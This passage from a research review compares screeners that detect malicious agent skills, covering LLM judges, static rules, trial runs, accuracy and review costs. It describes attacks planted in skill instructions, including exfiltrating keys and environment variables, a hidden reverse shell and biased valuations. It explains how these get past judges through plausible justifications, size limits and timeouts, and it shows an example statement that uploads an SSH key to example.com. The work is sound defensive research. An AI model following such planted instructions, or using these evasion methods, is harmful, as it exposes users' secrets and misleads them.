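| Outside the scope of a security review | 20 | 120 |
| No direct harm | 20 | 65 |
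| Acceptable once the user fixes the problem | 19 | – |
| Legitimate behaviour | – | 20 |
| No reason given | – | 29 |

The screener most often missed malicious skills because their packages contained no code to carry out the attack. A skill might tell the user to download a script from an outside site and run it. The script is not in the folder, so the screener finds nothing dangerous to execute. The ClawHavoc campaign worked this way. An agent can also carry out a written instruction without any script.

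When AI-Infra-Guard dismissed an attack, it was most often because it judged the attack to be outside its scope. For example, it found instructions in the financial-analysis skill to bias the agent's company valuations, but called them a compliance issue. Skill-vetter treated similar manipulation, such as another skill's instructions to favour one vendor in evaluations, as a quality issue. Both skills deceive users who rely on the agent's answers, even though neither steals passwords or damages files.

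Some attacks do their damage later. One skill's setup script changed the registry from which the computer would install future software packages. Skill-vetter identified the risk that this could bring in tampered packages, but passed the skill on the grounds that changing a setting caused no direct harm.

Whether a conditional approval counts as a miss depends partly on how misses are defined. The skill project-init contains a hook that downloads code and runs it without checking it. Skill-vetter told users to remove the hook or verify the code before installing the skill. Yang and colleagues counted this as a miss because the verdict did not block installation. A careful user who read the advice would have been protected, but a hub that acts only on the verdict would publish the skill unchanged.

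AI-Infra-Guard also dismissed an attack in the infrastructure-monitoring skill because it treated SKILL.md as trusted instructions. Zhao and colleagues point out that this assumption fails for skills, because the author may be the attacker. It makes sense when developers look for weaknesses in their own software, where the danger comes from outsiders.

Judges that give a single verdict make similar mistakes, although neither Wu, Li and Liu nor Hou and colleagues counted them by cause. Kimi passed a skill called botcoin as a well-documented blockchain game, but the skill's setup script sent environment variables to an outside server. Opus passed the presentation skill whose JavaScript file hides a reverse shell, with 0.95 confidence that it was safe. A confidence threshold would have caught that skill only if it required more than 0.95 confidence to pass.

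A judge needs to accept innocent explanations for behavior that could be malicious. A weather skill has a good reason to read its own API key, and a judge that rejected such reasons would block a large part of a hub. Attackers write their descriptions to supply the same kind of reason. Any remedy has to make the judge reject more of these false explanations without making it flag legitimate skills indiscriminately.

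### Three changes tested on the same skills

Three studies compared a plain judge with a modified screener on a shared set of skills. *The Devil Wears Markdown* added its evidence in two steps, and each step has its own row.

| Change | Malicious / benign skills | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| BIV: structured evidence and an override | 404 / 502 | 98.9% → 97.2% | 68.8% → 92.8% |
| SkillSieve: four questions instead of one | 89 / 311 | 100% → 75.2% | 59.6% → 85.4% |
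| *The Devil Wears Markdown*: evidence from a trial run | 80 / 60 | 72% → 93% | 68% → 79% |
| The same, with static findings added | 80 / 60 | 93% → 93% | 79% → 85% |

The rows are not a ranking, because the skills, labels and models differ between studies.

### An override that the judge cannot veto

BIV takes part of the decision away from the language model. Once it has extracted a skill's capabilities and data paths, it reaches a verdict in three steps:

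1. Opus reads the skill together with this evidence and calls it safe or malicious.
2. Fixed rules calculate a risk level from the evidence alone. The level is critical if, for example, the code downloads a file and runs it, or encodes data and sends it out. Otherwise it depends on the most serious undeclared capability or suspicious combination.
3. BIV flags the skill if Opus calls it malicious or if the risk level is high or critical.

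The presentation skill shows why the third step matters. Opus had evidence that the skill decodes a block of text and runs it as code, but still classified the skill as safe with a confidence of 0.82. Claude Sonnet 4.5 also classified it as safe, on the grounds that these capabilities were necessary for the skill's core function. BIV flagged the skill anyway because the risk level was high.

BIV caught 97 more malicious skills than the single call and raised 8 more false alarms. The two methods disagreed on 109 skills, and BIV was right about 99 of them. BIV caught 28 of the 44 pieces of real malware, twice as many as the single call, but still missed more than a third. The 95% confidence interval for its recall on this malware is 49% to 76%.

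BIV's eight extra false alarms would become many more on a large hub. Among the skills that came from hubs, BIV flagged 10 of 410 benign ones and the baseline flagged 2. On a hub of 100,000 skills, 160 of them malicious, BIV would catch about 51 more malicious skills than the baseline and raise 1,950 more false alarms, or 38 for each additional catch. Replacing VirusTotal with skill-vetter on the same hub would add 54 false alarms for each additional catch. A skill that BIV passed would have a 0.06% chance of being malicious, compared with 0.11% for one that the baseline passed.

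The test does not show how much of the gain comes from the override, because BIV's judge also had the structured evidence, which the baseline lacked, and Wu, Li and Liu did not test the two changes separately. The choice of judge also matters, as BIV caught 38 of the 44 with Sonnet 4.5 but only 24 with Gemini 3 Pro.

The override is also weakest on attacks written in prose. If only the instructions support a concern and there are fewer than two indicators, the rules cap the risk at medium and leave the final decision to Opus. This keeps a stray sentence from blocking a harmless skill, but Opus can still dismiss an attack because it has no code behind it, which was skill-vetter's most common reason for dismissing attacks.

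### Four questions instead of one

SkillSieve keeps the decision with the model but breaks up the question. The model answers four questions separately, each with a risk score from 0 to 1:

- Do the instructions match the skill's stated purpose?
- Does that purpose justify the permissions?
- Does the skill hide anything from the user?
- Do the scripts and commands do what SKILL.md describes?

Asking separate questions makes it less likely that a plausible purpose will decide the whole verdict. Kimi passed one skill described as an identity service when asked for a single verdict. When asked to compare the skill's purpose with its instructions, Kimi flagged the instructions to collect and send private keys. The question about scripts also exposed botcoin.

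In the first test, the four questions caught 76 of the 89 malicious skills, 23 more than the single prompt, but they also raised 25 false alarms, while the single prompt raised none. F1 therefore rose only from 0.75 to 0.80. The changed labels make the comparison even less certain, because some of the 23 additional catches may be skills that the later review considered benign. The human annotator also found the identity service hard to classify.

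The way SkillSieve combines the answers may explain some of the false alarms. Its formula is:

risk = 0.35 × purpose + 0.25 × permissions + 0.25 × hidden behaviour + 0.15 × scripts

A skill counts as high-risk if its total score is at least 0.4. Clear evidence on a single question is not enough, because a score of 1 on that question and 0 on the others gives a total of at most 0.35. But a skill that looks mildly suspicious on every question, scoring 0.4 on each, reaches the threshold. Cryptocurrency wallets fit this pattern because they normally handle private keys and call exchanges. Skills for wallets and decentralised finance accounted for roughly a third of the false alarms at this stage in the later test. Hou and colleagues suggest escalating a skill only when at least one question gets a high score.

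The later version sends high-risk skills to a jury of three models from different companies: GLM-5.1, Qwen3-235B and DeepSeek-V3.1. If they disagree, each reads the others' reasons and votes again. A skill passes only if all three label it safe. If they split without a majority for "malicious", the skill is held until a human reviews it.

On the revised set of 390 skills, the jury raised precision from 67.5% to 91.2%. The whole system caught 52 of 56 malicious skills and flagged 5 of 334 benign ones. Hou and colleagues report no single-prompt result for this set, so their results don't show how much better the system is than one model given a single prompt.

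### Evidence from a trial run

A judge that only reads a skill has to guess what will happen when an agent uses it. *The Devil Wears Markdown* gives the judge a record of an actual attempt:

1. Claude Opus 4.8 tries out the skill in an isolated container for up to five minutes, using harmless dummy files. Its instructions are to skip anything dangerous and to write down what it skipped and why.
2. Monitoring tools record system calls, network traffic and changes to files.
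3. Fixed rules turn the record into a score from 0 to 100. Harmful behaviour that actually ran gets full weight. A dangerous command that Opus refused to run still scores at least 85 if the command really is in the skill. A general warning from Opus with no passage to support it scores at most 25.
4. A group of agents led by Qwen3.5 122B weighs the skill's text and the evidence, and gives a verdict.

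The third step deals with attacks that a judge might dismiss because nothing bad has happened yet. A refusal counts as evidence if someone can trace it to the skill's text.

When the agents read only the skill, they caught 54 of 80 malicious skills and flagged 21 of 60 benign ones, for an F1 of 0.70. When they also had the record of the trial run, they caught 63 malicious skills and flagged 5 benign ones, for an F1 of 0.85. Adding findings from static rules let them catch 68 with no more false alarms, which raised F1 to 0.89. The added evidence reduced both missed skills and false alarms, whereas the override and the four questions increased recall but also caused more false alarms. SkillScope also did much better when it ran skills.

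When the agents had static findings without the trial run, they flagged only 3 benign skills but caught just 28 of the 80 malicious ones, about half as many as with no extra evidence. The rules behind these findings came from general malware scanning, and one of the two rule sets produced more alerts on benign skills (11.7 on average) than on malicious ones (6.3). The agents may have taken the lack of a convincing code finding as a sign that a skill was safe. Extra evidence can therefore make a judge more lenient if it covers the wrong part of the package.

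Some of the gain from the trial run may come from getting another capable model's opinion rather than from running the skill. Opus 4.8 reads each skill before trying it, and its refusals go into the record the agents see. A fairer comparison would give the agents Opus's comments without the trial. The sample is also small. Each skill was run once, and the rise from 0.85 to 0.89 comes from five skills.

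The judge can still misread the extra evidence. The skill research-lookup uses an API key and includes a vendor's installation command. Its trial run scored 27.5, below the threshold of 35 for malicious behaviour, and one finding in the report described the command as harmless setup. Even so, the final verdict was malicious, with a score of 92.

### Rewriting the judge's instructions

Yang and colleagues tried the easiest remedy, adding two passages to skill-vetter's instructions. The first tells the model not to use any of skill-vetter's four usual reasons to dismiss an attack it has identified. If the package has no code, for example, the model should consider what would happen if someone followed the package's instructions. The second lists innocent explanations for the most common false alarms, such as a skill that logs in to its own service.

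They tested the result on new skills from MalSkillBench and SkillTrustBench, with 150 malicious and 150 benign skills from each. They also tested it on 154 malicious and 112 benign skills from SkillSafetyBench, which they had not used in their error analysis. Each figure, before and after the change, is an average over three runs.

| Dataset | Judge | Misses | False alarms | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
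| MalSkillBench | Qwen3.6 | 22.7 → 19.7 | 12.7 → 7.7 | 0.878 → 0.905 |
| MalSkillBench | GPT-5.4 | 10.7 → 6.3 | 66.3 → 8.7 | 0.784 → 0.950 |
| MalSkillBench | DeepSeek-V4 | 20.3 → 14.3 | 19.3 → 5.0 | 0.867 → 0.933 |
| SkillTrustBench | Qwen3.6 | 8.7 → 7.3 | 5.7 → 2.7 | 0.952 → 0.966 |
| SkillTrustBench | GPT-5.4 | 1.3 → 2.0 | 53.0 → 15.0 | 0.846 → 0.946 |
| SkillTrustBench | DeepSeek-V4 | 5.7 → 6.3 | 5.7 → 2.3 | 0.962 → 0.971 |
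| SkillSafetyBench | Qwen3.6 | 109.3 → 114.3 | 1.7 → 0.7 | 0.445 → 0.402 |
| SkillSafetyBench | GPT-5.4 | 52.3 → 32.3 | 7.7 → 1.7 | 0.772 → 0.877 |
| SkillSafetyBench | DeepSeek-V4 | 103.0 → 65.3 | 0.3 → 0.3 | 0.496 → 0.723 |

F1 improved in eight of the nine settings. On MalSkillBench, GPT-5.4 missed fewer malicious skills and raised far fewer false alarms. A judge can therefore reduce both kinds of error before it has to trade one for the other. Misses rose in three settings, but in two of them the increase was less than one skill.

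The exception is Qwen3.6 on SkillSafetyBench, where misses rose by five. Before the change, the model had wrongly flagged fewer than 2 of the 112 benign skills, so the innocent explanations in the second passage had almost no false alarms to correct. They may instead have given the model more reasons to pass attacks. The rise could also be chance, because the number of misses varied between runs with a standard deviation of 5.0 before the change and 3.2 after it. Yang and colleagues tested the two passages only together, so it is unclear whether the first alone would have helped.

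Skill-vetter also missed many attacks with revised instructions. On SkillSafetyBench, the revised version still missed 74% of malicious skills with Qwen3.6, 42% with DeepSeek-V4 and 21% with GPT-5.4. DeepSeek-V4's improvement was the largest in the table, but it is uncertain because the model's misses varied between runs with a standard deviation of 22.

The two passages can conflict. Under the second, an archive the model has not inspected is a reason for uncertainty but not enough by itself to justify rejection. ClawHavoc's Windows malware came in an archive that scanners could not open, so the model has to classify the instruction to download it as either an attack, which the first passage covers, or something it could not check.

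### Treating instructions as program code

Zhao and colleagues go further than BIV and give the language model no say in the verdict. Their screener, SCS, uses the model as a translator. The model turns each instruction that involves an operation into one or more simple program statements, chosen from a limited set that covers actions such as reading files, running commands and sending data. An instruction to read the user's private login key and upload it becomes:

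```
v0 = read_file("~/.ssh/id_rsa")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
```

The variable v0 shows that the uploaded data is the key. SCS links these statements to the skill's scripts in a single graph and follows each piece of data through it, tracking where the data came from, how sensitive it is and what the skill can do with it. It then applies fixed rules to determine whether the combination is dangerous.

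This suits attacks split between prose and code, such as the copied slide-making skill with the added backup step. SCS can connect the instruction with the script and detect that the user's presentation is sent to an outside server, whereas a model reading the same skill might treat "backup" as a sufficient reason for sending it.

SCS caught 95.2% of the malicious skills in its test, but its false-positive rate was about 24% because its rules flag suspicious behavior regardless of any stated justification. Like a skill that steals data, a legitimate backup tool reads a user's file and sends it to a server, so the data flow alone may not distinguish the two.

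*The Devil Wears Markdown* describes MalSkills as a system that extracts sensitive operations from a skill's instructions, code and metadata and connects them in a graph. MalSkills then interprets the graph using both fixed patterns and a language model's reasoning. Zhao and colleagues, whose own system competes with it, object that the verdict still depends heavily on the model. However, this design makes it possible to recognise a legitimate backup tool.

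SCS still depends on its model to translate instructions into the graph. The five models translated over 92% of instruction steps correctly in a test against human annotations, but if a model treats a harmful step as description, the step never enters the graph and no rule can catch it. Some attacks also have no operation to translate. An instruction to bias a company valuation doesn't involve reading a secret or contacting a server, so SCS would probably miss financial-analysis, as AI-Infra-Guard did.

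## What a review costs, and what quotas and budgets allow

A judge that reads more of a skill, or answers more questions about it, uses more tokens, and a hub pays for them on every submission. Yang and colleagues recorded how many tokens and seconds each model-based screener used per skill in their test. They converted the tokens to dollars using prices from OpenRouter, which sells access to many models.

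### Tokens, seconds and dollars per skill

| Screener | Judge | Tokens | Seconds | Cost | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | Qwen3.6 | 11,300 | 69.3 | $0.0004 | 0.919 |
| skill-scanner | DeepSeek-V4 | 9,400 | 68.9 | $0.0013 | 0.914 |
| skill-scanner | GPT-5.4 | 8,200 | 21.6 | $0.031 | 0.885 |
| SkillSpector | Qwen3.6 | 73,200 | 160.0 | $0.0032 | 0.793 |
| SkillSpector | DeepSeek-V4 | 65,600 | 134.4 | $0.010 | 0.890 |
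| SkillSpector | GPT-5.4 | 49,300 | 20.5 | $0.16 | 0.902 |
| skill-vetter | Qwen3.6 | 95,400 | 77.8 | $0.0012 | 0.943 |
| skill-vetter | DeepSeek-V4 | 115,600 | 137.3 | $0.0072 | 0.938 |
| skill-vetter | GPT-5.4 | 175,600 | 69.7 | $0.51 | 0.879 |
| AI-Infra-Guard | Qwen3.6 | 306,200 | 115.9 | $0.0047 | 0.891 |
| AI-Infra-Guard | DeepSeek-V4 | 209,000 | 271.0 | $0.017 | 0.864 |
| AI-Infra-Guard | GPT-5.4 | 169,500 | 109.5 | $0.55 | 0.898 |

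Yang and colleagues ran Qwen3.6 and DeepSeek-V4 on four of their own graphics processors, so the dollar figures for those two models are what a provider would have charged, and the times depend on that hardware.

AI-Infra-Guard with GPT-5.4 costs almost 1,400 times as much per skill as skill-scanner with Qwen3.6. Most of the gap comes from the model's price. GPT-5.4 costs 76 to 237 times as much per token as Qwen3.6, depending on the screener, while token counts in the table differ by at most a factor of 37. The rest comes from the screeners' designs, since skill-scanner sends a single prompt and AI-Infra-Guard lets its agent take up to 80 steps in each of three stages.

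Static rules use no tokens and usually finish faster than model reviews. ClawHub-Mod takes 0.05 seconds per skill, SkillSpector's rules take 1 second and skill-scanner's take 4. The exception is skillscan-security, which averages 25 seconds without calling a model. That is longer than SkillSpector takes with GPT-5.4.

### Spending more did not raise F1

Across the twelve combinations, Yang and colleagues found a rank correlation with F1 of −0.23 for tokens and −0.35 for time. The same calculation for dollars gives −0.43. A value of 1 would mean that combinations that used more always scored higher, and −1 that they always scored lower. With only twelve combinations, chance could produce values of this size, so the results don't show that cheap reviews are better, but they give a hub little reason to assume that expensive reviews are.

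The effect of a more expensive model differs by screener. SkillSpector costs 51 times as much with GPT-5.4 as with Qwen3.6, and its recall rises from 68.7% to 94.2%. Skill-vetter costs 436 times as much with GPT-5.4, but its F1 falls because the model raises so many false alarms. This is partly due to the screener's instructions. With revised instructions, GPT-5.4 does better than Qwen3.6 on two of three test sets. An expensive model may therefore be worth its price if the screener gives it better instructions.

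Shen, Feng and colleagues (2026) also measured token use in *Sealing the Audit-Runtime Gap for LLM Skills*, which presents SIGIL, a registry from which agents load only the exact version of a skill that auditors approved. The researchers ran four model-based audit methods on 100 skills and compared the token counts with 15 million tokens, their figure for the monthly quota of a $20 GPT subscription. The last column divides that quota by the tokens per skill to give the number of skills it would cover each month.

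| Audit method | Tokens per skill | Share of monthly quota | Audits per month |
|---|---|---|---|
| Manifest (checks permissions) | 34,870 | 0.23% | 430 |
| LLM (a general model review) | 84,020 | 0.56% | 178 |
| SkillScan | 137,700 | 0.92% | 108 |
| Security Scanner | 418,790 | 2.79% | 35 |

Shen and colleagues call this overhead minor, which is fair for a developer who audits one skill, but the percentages apply to each skill. A hub with 500 submissions a day would use up about 35 subscriptions a month with the manifest check and 419 with Security Scanner. SIGIL also requires at least five auditors per skill, which could multiply the cost.

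Here too, the method that used the most tokens was not the most accurate. SkillScan (a different tool from skillscan-security) had the highest accuracy of any single method, 96.0% on 1,079 skills. Security Scanner used three times as many tokens as SkillScan and missed many malicious skills. When Shen and colleagues removed Security Scanner from a committee of six methods, the committee's F1 fell only from 98.3% to 98.2%. The accuracy figures are probably too high for some methods, because the researchers used scanner results to help choose and label the skills.

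### The smallest of three limits

Money, tokens and time each limit how many skills a hub can review in a day, and the smallest limit decides:

reviews per day = min(B / c, Q / t, W × 86,400 / s)

B is the daily budget and c is the cost per review. Q is the number of tokens the hub may use per day and t is the number each review uses. W is the number of workers, each handling one review at a time, and s is the number of seconds a review takes. A day has 86,400 seconds.

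Suppose a hub has one worker and a daily limit of $20 and 50 million tokens. With skill-vetter and Qwen3.6, it could run 524 reviews a day before running out of tokens, although the money would pay for about 17,200 and the worker could finish 1,110. With AI-Infra-Guard and GPT-5.4, it could run 36 before running out of money, although the tokens would allow 294 and the worker could finish 789. A larger token quota would help only in the first case.

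The next table applies Yang and colleagues' averages to 500 submissions a day and to one rescan of the 85,130 skills they found on ClawHub.

| Screener and judge | 500 submissions: cost | Worker hours | Rescan: cost | Days for one worker |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner, Qwen3.6 | $0.20 | 9.6 | $34 | 68 |
| skill-vetter, Qwen3.6 | $0.58 | 10.8 | $99 | 77 |
| AI-Infra-Guard, DeepSeek-V4 | $8.30 | 37.6 | $1,413 | 267 |
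| SkillSpector, GPT-5.4 | $81 | 2.8 | $13,808 | 20 |
| AI-Infra-Guard, GPT-5.4 | $277 | 15.2 | $47,080 | 108 |

With a cheap model, the main constraint on a rescan is time. One worker running skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 takes 77.8 seconds per skill, so a rescan takes 77 days and costs $99. In principle, 77 workers could finish in a day for the same total cost. On a hub's own hardware, however, simultaneous reviews share the same processors and eventually slow each other down.

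A hub that buys tokens from a provider can reach its per-minute quota well before its daily one. An average AI-Infra-Guard review with Qwen3.6 uses about 158,500 tokens a minute while it runs. Under a quota of a million tokens a minute, six such reviews could run at once, but a seventh would exceed the quota.

Screeners also depend on other outside services. SkillSpector looks up known flaws in a skill's dependencies on OSV.dev, a free vulnerability database. According to NVIDIA, it sends all the dependencies in one request and keeps the answers for an hour. If it can't reach the database, it finishes the scan using a small built-in list, which covers far fewer flaws.

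The formula uses averages, and individual reviews can take far longer. AI-Infra-Guard took 1,000 seconds or more per skill with Qwen3.6's reasoning switched on, and at that rate one worker could review at most 86 skills a day.

### When submissions exceed capacity

A queue can absorb a temporary surge, but it keeps growing if the shortfall is permanent. Suppose the hub with 500 submissions a day has one worker running skill-vetter with Qwen3.6, and enough money and tokens. If an extra 3,000 skills arrive in one day, 2,390 are still waiting that evening, and the worker needs almost four more days to catch up. If the hub can instead review only 400 of its 500 daily submissions, 3,000 skills are waiting after a month, and a new one waits more than a week.

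The hub also has to decide whether users can install skills that are still in the queue. If it allows this, a queue of 3,000 skills would expose users to about 5 malicious ones at a prevalence of 0.16%, or 360 at the 12% that Koi found on ClawHub during the ClawHavoc campaign. Mass uploads of malicious skills also lengthen the queue, so allowing installs before review is most dangerous during an attack.

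Holding skills back until the review is finished protects users but makes authors wait. A specification from CNOE, an open-source project for software platforms, takes this approach with Cisco's skill-scanner. The scanner checks skills from outside hubs before they enter the catalogue, and checks a user's own skill when the user saves or publishes it. In Yang and colleagues' test, the wait would have been about 4 seconds with static rules alone and between 22 and 69 seconds with a model. With a long queue, the wait could be days, and an attacker could create such a queue by submitting thousands of junk skills.

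SIGIL makes publishers pay for the review, which would discourage this kind of flooding. The fee rises with the length of the skill and the number of auditors. A review starts only once enough auditors have claimed the skill. If too few do, the reward rises by 25% of its original value for each waiting period. Even so, Shen and colleagues acknowledge that timely reviews depend on attracting enough auditors. The fee could also drive away hobbyists who publish free skills.

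A hub can instead make each review cheaper, for example by calling the judge only for skills that a cheaper filter has flagged or using a smaller model. ClawHub's *ClawScan security* (2026), an April review of one skill, lists gpt-5-mini as the judge.

Reading less of the skill saves money too. CodeRabbit, a code-review service, runs SkillSpector only on changed files with certain names, such as SKILL.md, and switches the model off. CodeRabbit presents this setup as a security restriction, but the setup also avoids all model costs. SkillSpector doesn't scan a skill's scripts, because their names aren't on the list. It also checks each file separately, so it can't connect an instruction in one file with an action in another.

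### Skills that are too long for the judge

Screeners limit how much text they send to a model, which keeps costs down and prevents the prompt from exceeding the model's context window, the most text it can process at once. For Cisco's skill-scanner, the *Scan Policy Guide* gives these defaults:

| Input | Limit in characters |
|---|---|
| Instructions in SKILL.md | 20,000 |
| Each code file | 15,000 |
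| Each referenced file | 10,000 |
| Whole prompt | 100,000 |

Skill-scanner omits any file or instruction text that exceeds its limit, rather than truncating it, and adds a note to the result. If a skill's instructions exceed 20,000 characters, the judge therefore receives none of them. The optional meta-analyzer's limits are three times as high.

In Yang and colleagues' test, skill-scanner with a model did not identify the attack at all in 66 cases, and this limit caused 39 of them. Those 39 are about a fifth of all its misses. A better judge would not have caught them, because it would not have received the instructions either.

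The judge could read only the first 20,000 characters of long instructions, but an attacker could then put the harmful step after that point. Reading everything is safer and often affordable. At the average price per token in skill-scanner's reviews, reading 60,000 characters, or roughly 15,000 tokens, would cost about $0.0005 with Qwen3.6 or $0.06 with GPT-5.4. The limit therefore saves almost no money with Qwen3.6. However, a model may more easily overlook one harmful line in a very long prompt, so a hub would need to test a higher limit before relying on it.

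Static analysis has size limits as well. By default, skill-scanner does not load files over 10 MB for content analysis, and the strict preset lowers this to 5 MB. Cisco AI Defense's *Scan Policies* recommends the strict preset for untrusted skills, although it skips files between 5 and 10 MB that the default would load. The strict preset does report any file over 2 MB as oversized, compared with 5 MB by default. According to Cisco, the scanner stops unpacking an archive after 50 MB or 500 files and may leave the rest unread.

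Yang and colleagues found that a malicious skill, omnicogg, got past the static rules of SkillSpector and skillscan-security because its README file exceeded their size limits. ClawHub-Mod missed the same skill because it excluded the README as invalid text.

A hub could refuse any skill that its screener cannot read in full. Developers of long but legitimate skills would then have to shorten or divide them, but attackers could no longer easily hide malicious content in the part that goes unread.

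### Reviews that end without a verdict

Yang and colleagues limited skillscan-security to 60 seconds per skill and SkillSpector to 900. Their accuracy figures exclude skills on which a screener timed out or crashed. This makes little difference for the model-based screeners, none of which failed on more than 5 skills. But skillscan-security returned no verdict on 53 skills, all of them malicious. Most of these failures were probably timeouts, since the tool averaged 25 seconds per skill. Counting all 53 as misses lowers its recall from 85.1% to 80.0%.

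A hub needs a separate rule for reviews that don't finish. Treating them as passes lets an attacker get a skill published by making it slow to scan, but treating them as blocks can keep out large skills from honest authors. Retrying with a longer time limit avoids both problems in some cases but uses more of the day's review capacity.

A review can also finish with parts missing. A model sometimes returns a reply that the screener cannot interpret, for instance because it was cut off at the length limit. According to NVIDIA's *SkillSpector v2.9.3* (2026), when repeated attempts fail, SkillSpector now keeps its existing findings, records the affected work as skipped and marks the analysis as incomplete. A hub has to check for that mark, because a low risk score may simply mean that part of the analysis was skipped.

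### Reusing verdicts and reviewing updates

A hub can avoid paying to review the same skill twice by storing each verdict with a fingerprint, a short code calculated from the package's file paths and contents. Yang and colleagues used such fingerprints to remove copies from their test data. With stored verdicts, a hub would have needed only 193 reviews for the 703 skills that Guo and colleagues collected. Reusing verdicts also stops an attacker from resubmitting an identical package until the judge happens to approve it, although changing a single character produces a new fingerprint.

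The fingerprint should cover the whole package. If a hub reused verdicts for individual files, an attacker could publish a harmless skill with an upload script and later add an instruction to send the user's files through it. The script would keep its old verdict even though its role had changed. Stored verdicts also go out of date when the hub changes its model, prompt or rules. A fingerprint of the package doesn't cover files on outside servers, where the ClawHavoc malware was hosted.

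A simple schedule can limit repeated scans on a user's machine. Cisco AI Defense's editor extension scans skills at startup unless a scan has run in the past 60 minutes, and scans again whenever a skill file changes.

SIGIL treats every update as a new submission. The previously approved version stays available until the new one passes, so a long queue doesn't interrupt anyone's work. But a security fix waits in the same queue, so users keep installing the flawed version until the auditors approve the fix.

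Periodically rescanning existing skills can easily cost more than reviewing new ones. To rescan all 85,130 of its skills every 30 days, ClawHub would have to review about 2,840 a day in addition to the 500 new ones. Running all these reviews through Skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 would take just over three workers and cost about $4 a day. The same reviews would cost about $1,850 a day using AI-Infra-Guard with GPT-5.4.

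### The human time behind each alarm

The model's bill leaves out the people who check its alarms. If a hub has someone check every flagged skill, the average cost per submission is:

cost per submission = cost of the review + share of skills flagged × cost of checking one alarm

Suppose checking an alarm takes ten minutes and a reviewer costs $40 an hour. Each alarm then costs $6.67 to check. At a prevalence of 0.16%, skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 would flag about 32 of 500 submissions a day, almost all of them harmless, and the reviewer would spend 5.4 hours checking them. The cost per submission would be about $0.43, including roughly a tenth of a cent for the model.

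Rescanning the hub would cost $99 in model fees and produce about 5,500 alarms, which would take one person 914 hours, or nearly 23 working weeks, to check. Checking SkillSpector's recommendations would take far more work. It advised against installing 45.8% of skills on ClawHub. At that rate, 500 new skills a day would produce 229 warnings, which would take 38 hours to check.

Publishers also spend time responding to alarms. NVIDIA advises them to change the description or the code when the two don't match, and to upgrade a vulnerable dependency or document why it is acceptable. A publisher may spend longer resolving a false alarm than a reviewer would have spent dismissing it.

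A more expensive model can save money overall if it raises fewer false alarms. Replacing Qwen3.6 with GPT-5.4 in AI-Infra-Guard costs about $55 more per 100 skills and avoids about 5 false alarms, based on the false-positive rates in Yang and colleagues' test. That is roughly $11 per avoided alarm, or 16 minutes of a $40-an-hour reviewer's time, so GPT-5.4 would save money only if checking an alarm took longer than 16 minutes. Switching to DeepSeek-V4 instead avoids about 6 false alarms per 100 skills for an extra $1.20, but lowers recall from 87.5% to 79.8%.

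## Putting a cheap filter before an expensive judge

A hub can cut its screening costs by running a cheap filter on every skill and sending only the suspicious ones to the judge. The filter can be a set of static rules, a small language model or any other check that costs much less than the judge. The hub saves the cost of a judge call on every skill the filter clears, but any malicious skill the filter clears by mistake never reaches the judge.

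### Cost and recall with two stages

Let c_f be the cost of running the filter on one skill, c_j the cost of one review by the judge, and q the share of skills that the filter passes on. The average cost per skill is:

cost = c_f + q × c_j

The filter saves money only if c_f is less than (1 − q) × c_j. Static rules cost almost nothing, so they nearly always save money. A filter that uses a language model has to discard more skills. For example, skill-scanner with Qwen3.6 costs about a third as much per skill as skill-vetter with the same model, so it would have to discard more than a third of all skills to save money.

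The share passed on depends on the prevalence p, the filter's recall r_f and its false-positive rate f_f:

q = p × r_f + (1 − p) × f_f

When malicious skills are rare, the filter's false-positive rate determines most of the cost. As with any two checks that must both flag a skill, the recalls multiply:

recall = r_f × r_j

Here r_j is the judge's recall on the malicious skills it receives, which may differ from its recall on all malicious skills.

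Take a hub of 100,000 skills, 160 of them malicious, and a free filter that passes on 20% of the benign ones. If the judge charges one cent per review, the bill falls from $1,000 to about $200. The number of malicious skills caught depends on both stages:

| Filter's recall | Judge's recall on what it receives | Malicious skills caught |
|---|---|---|
| 100% | 90% | 144 |
| 95% | 90% | 137 |
| 95% | 100% | 152 |
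| 80% | 90% | 115 |
| 80% | 100% | 128 |

With the 80% filter, even a perfect judge catches only 128, fewer than an ordinary judge catches with the 95% filter. The whole system's recall therefore can't exceed the filter's recall.

Hou and colleagues apply the cost formula to SkillSieve, whose first stage they tuned to discard no malicious skill in their test. That stage passes on 14% of the skills on ClawHub, and the later stages cost about $0.04 for each of these, or $0.006 averaged over all skills. They estimate that a single model call would cost about $0.01 per skill. The filter discards 86% of the skills, but the cost falls by only 40% because the later stages are four times as expensive as a single call. If the filter passed on more than a quarter of the skills, SkillSieve would cost more than making a single call for every skill.

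### How many skills to pass on

If a hub has a budget B for N skills, the cost formula gives the largest share it can afford to pass on:

q = (B / N − c_f) / c_j

With $20 a day for 500 submissions, a free filter and a judge that costs $0.55 per review, the hub can send 7.3% of submissions, or 36 skills a day, to the judge. It should send the 36 that the filter scores as most suspicious.

*Signed Rescue Routing* (2026) describes how to do this when a small language model hands some requests to a large one. If all the requests are available at once, the system sorts them by score and passes on the top ones. If they arrive one at a time, it passes on those that score above a threshold, which it keeps updating so that the desired share of recent requests would have exceeded it. When some requests cost more than others, it ranks them by expected gain divided by cost. On a hub, this would rank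 short skills higher because they cost less to judge, so an author could push a malicious skill down the ranking by making it longer.

Reviewing a fixed share of submissions keeps the bill constant but can fail during an attack. Koi found that 12% of skills across ClawHub were malicious during ClawHavoc. If the same were true of the 500 submissions, 60 would be malicious and the judge would review only 36, so even a perfect ranking would leave 24 malicious skills unreviewed. A fixed threshold would send the judge every skill that looked suspicious enough, but the hub would have to spend more or let the queue grow.

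### Locate-and-Judge

A filter can also work within a skill, discarding most of its text and passing the rest to the judge. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* presents such a system, Locate-and-Judge. It is based on the idea that an agent will follow a hidden instruction only if the instruction attracts the attention of the model that reads it. Attention here means the weights that determine how much each token influences a language model's processing of another.

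The system works in five steps:

1. A parser splits the skill into spans along its structure, such as headings, paragraphs, list items and code blocks. The skills in the laboratory test had about 73 spans each on average.
2. Qwen2.5-0.5B-Instruct, a model with 0.5 billion parameters, reads the whole skill. Its prompt asks it to understand the instructions that determine the agent's behaviour, and tells it not to judge whether they are malicious. The system ignores any answer and records only the attention weights.
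3. Each token in the skill gets a score, which is the average attention it receives from the tokens that follow the skill text in the prompt. The average covers all attention heads in the model's last four layers. A span's score is the sum of its tokens' scores, and the system keeps the K spans with the highest scores.
4. The judge, DeepSeek-V4-Flash, reads each of these spans with a little surrounding text and estimates the probability that it contains a malicious instruction.
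5. The system flags the skill if the highest of these probabilities exceeds a threshold. The researchers set the threshold on 151 separate skills, 31 of them malicious, so that it produced no false alarms there.

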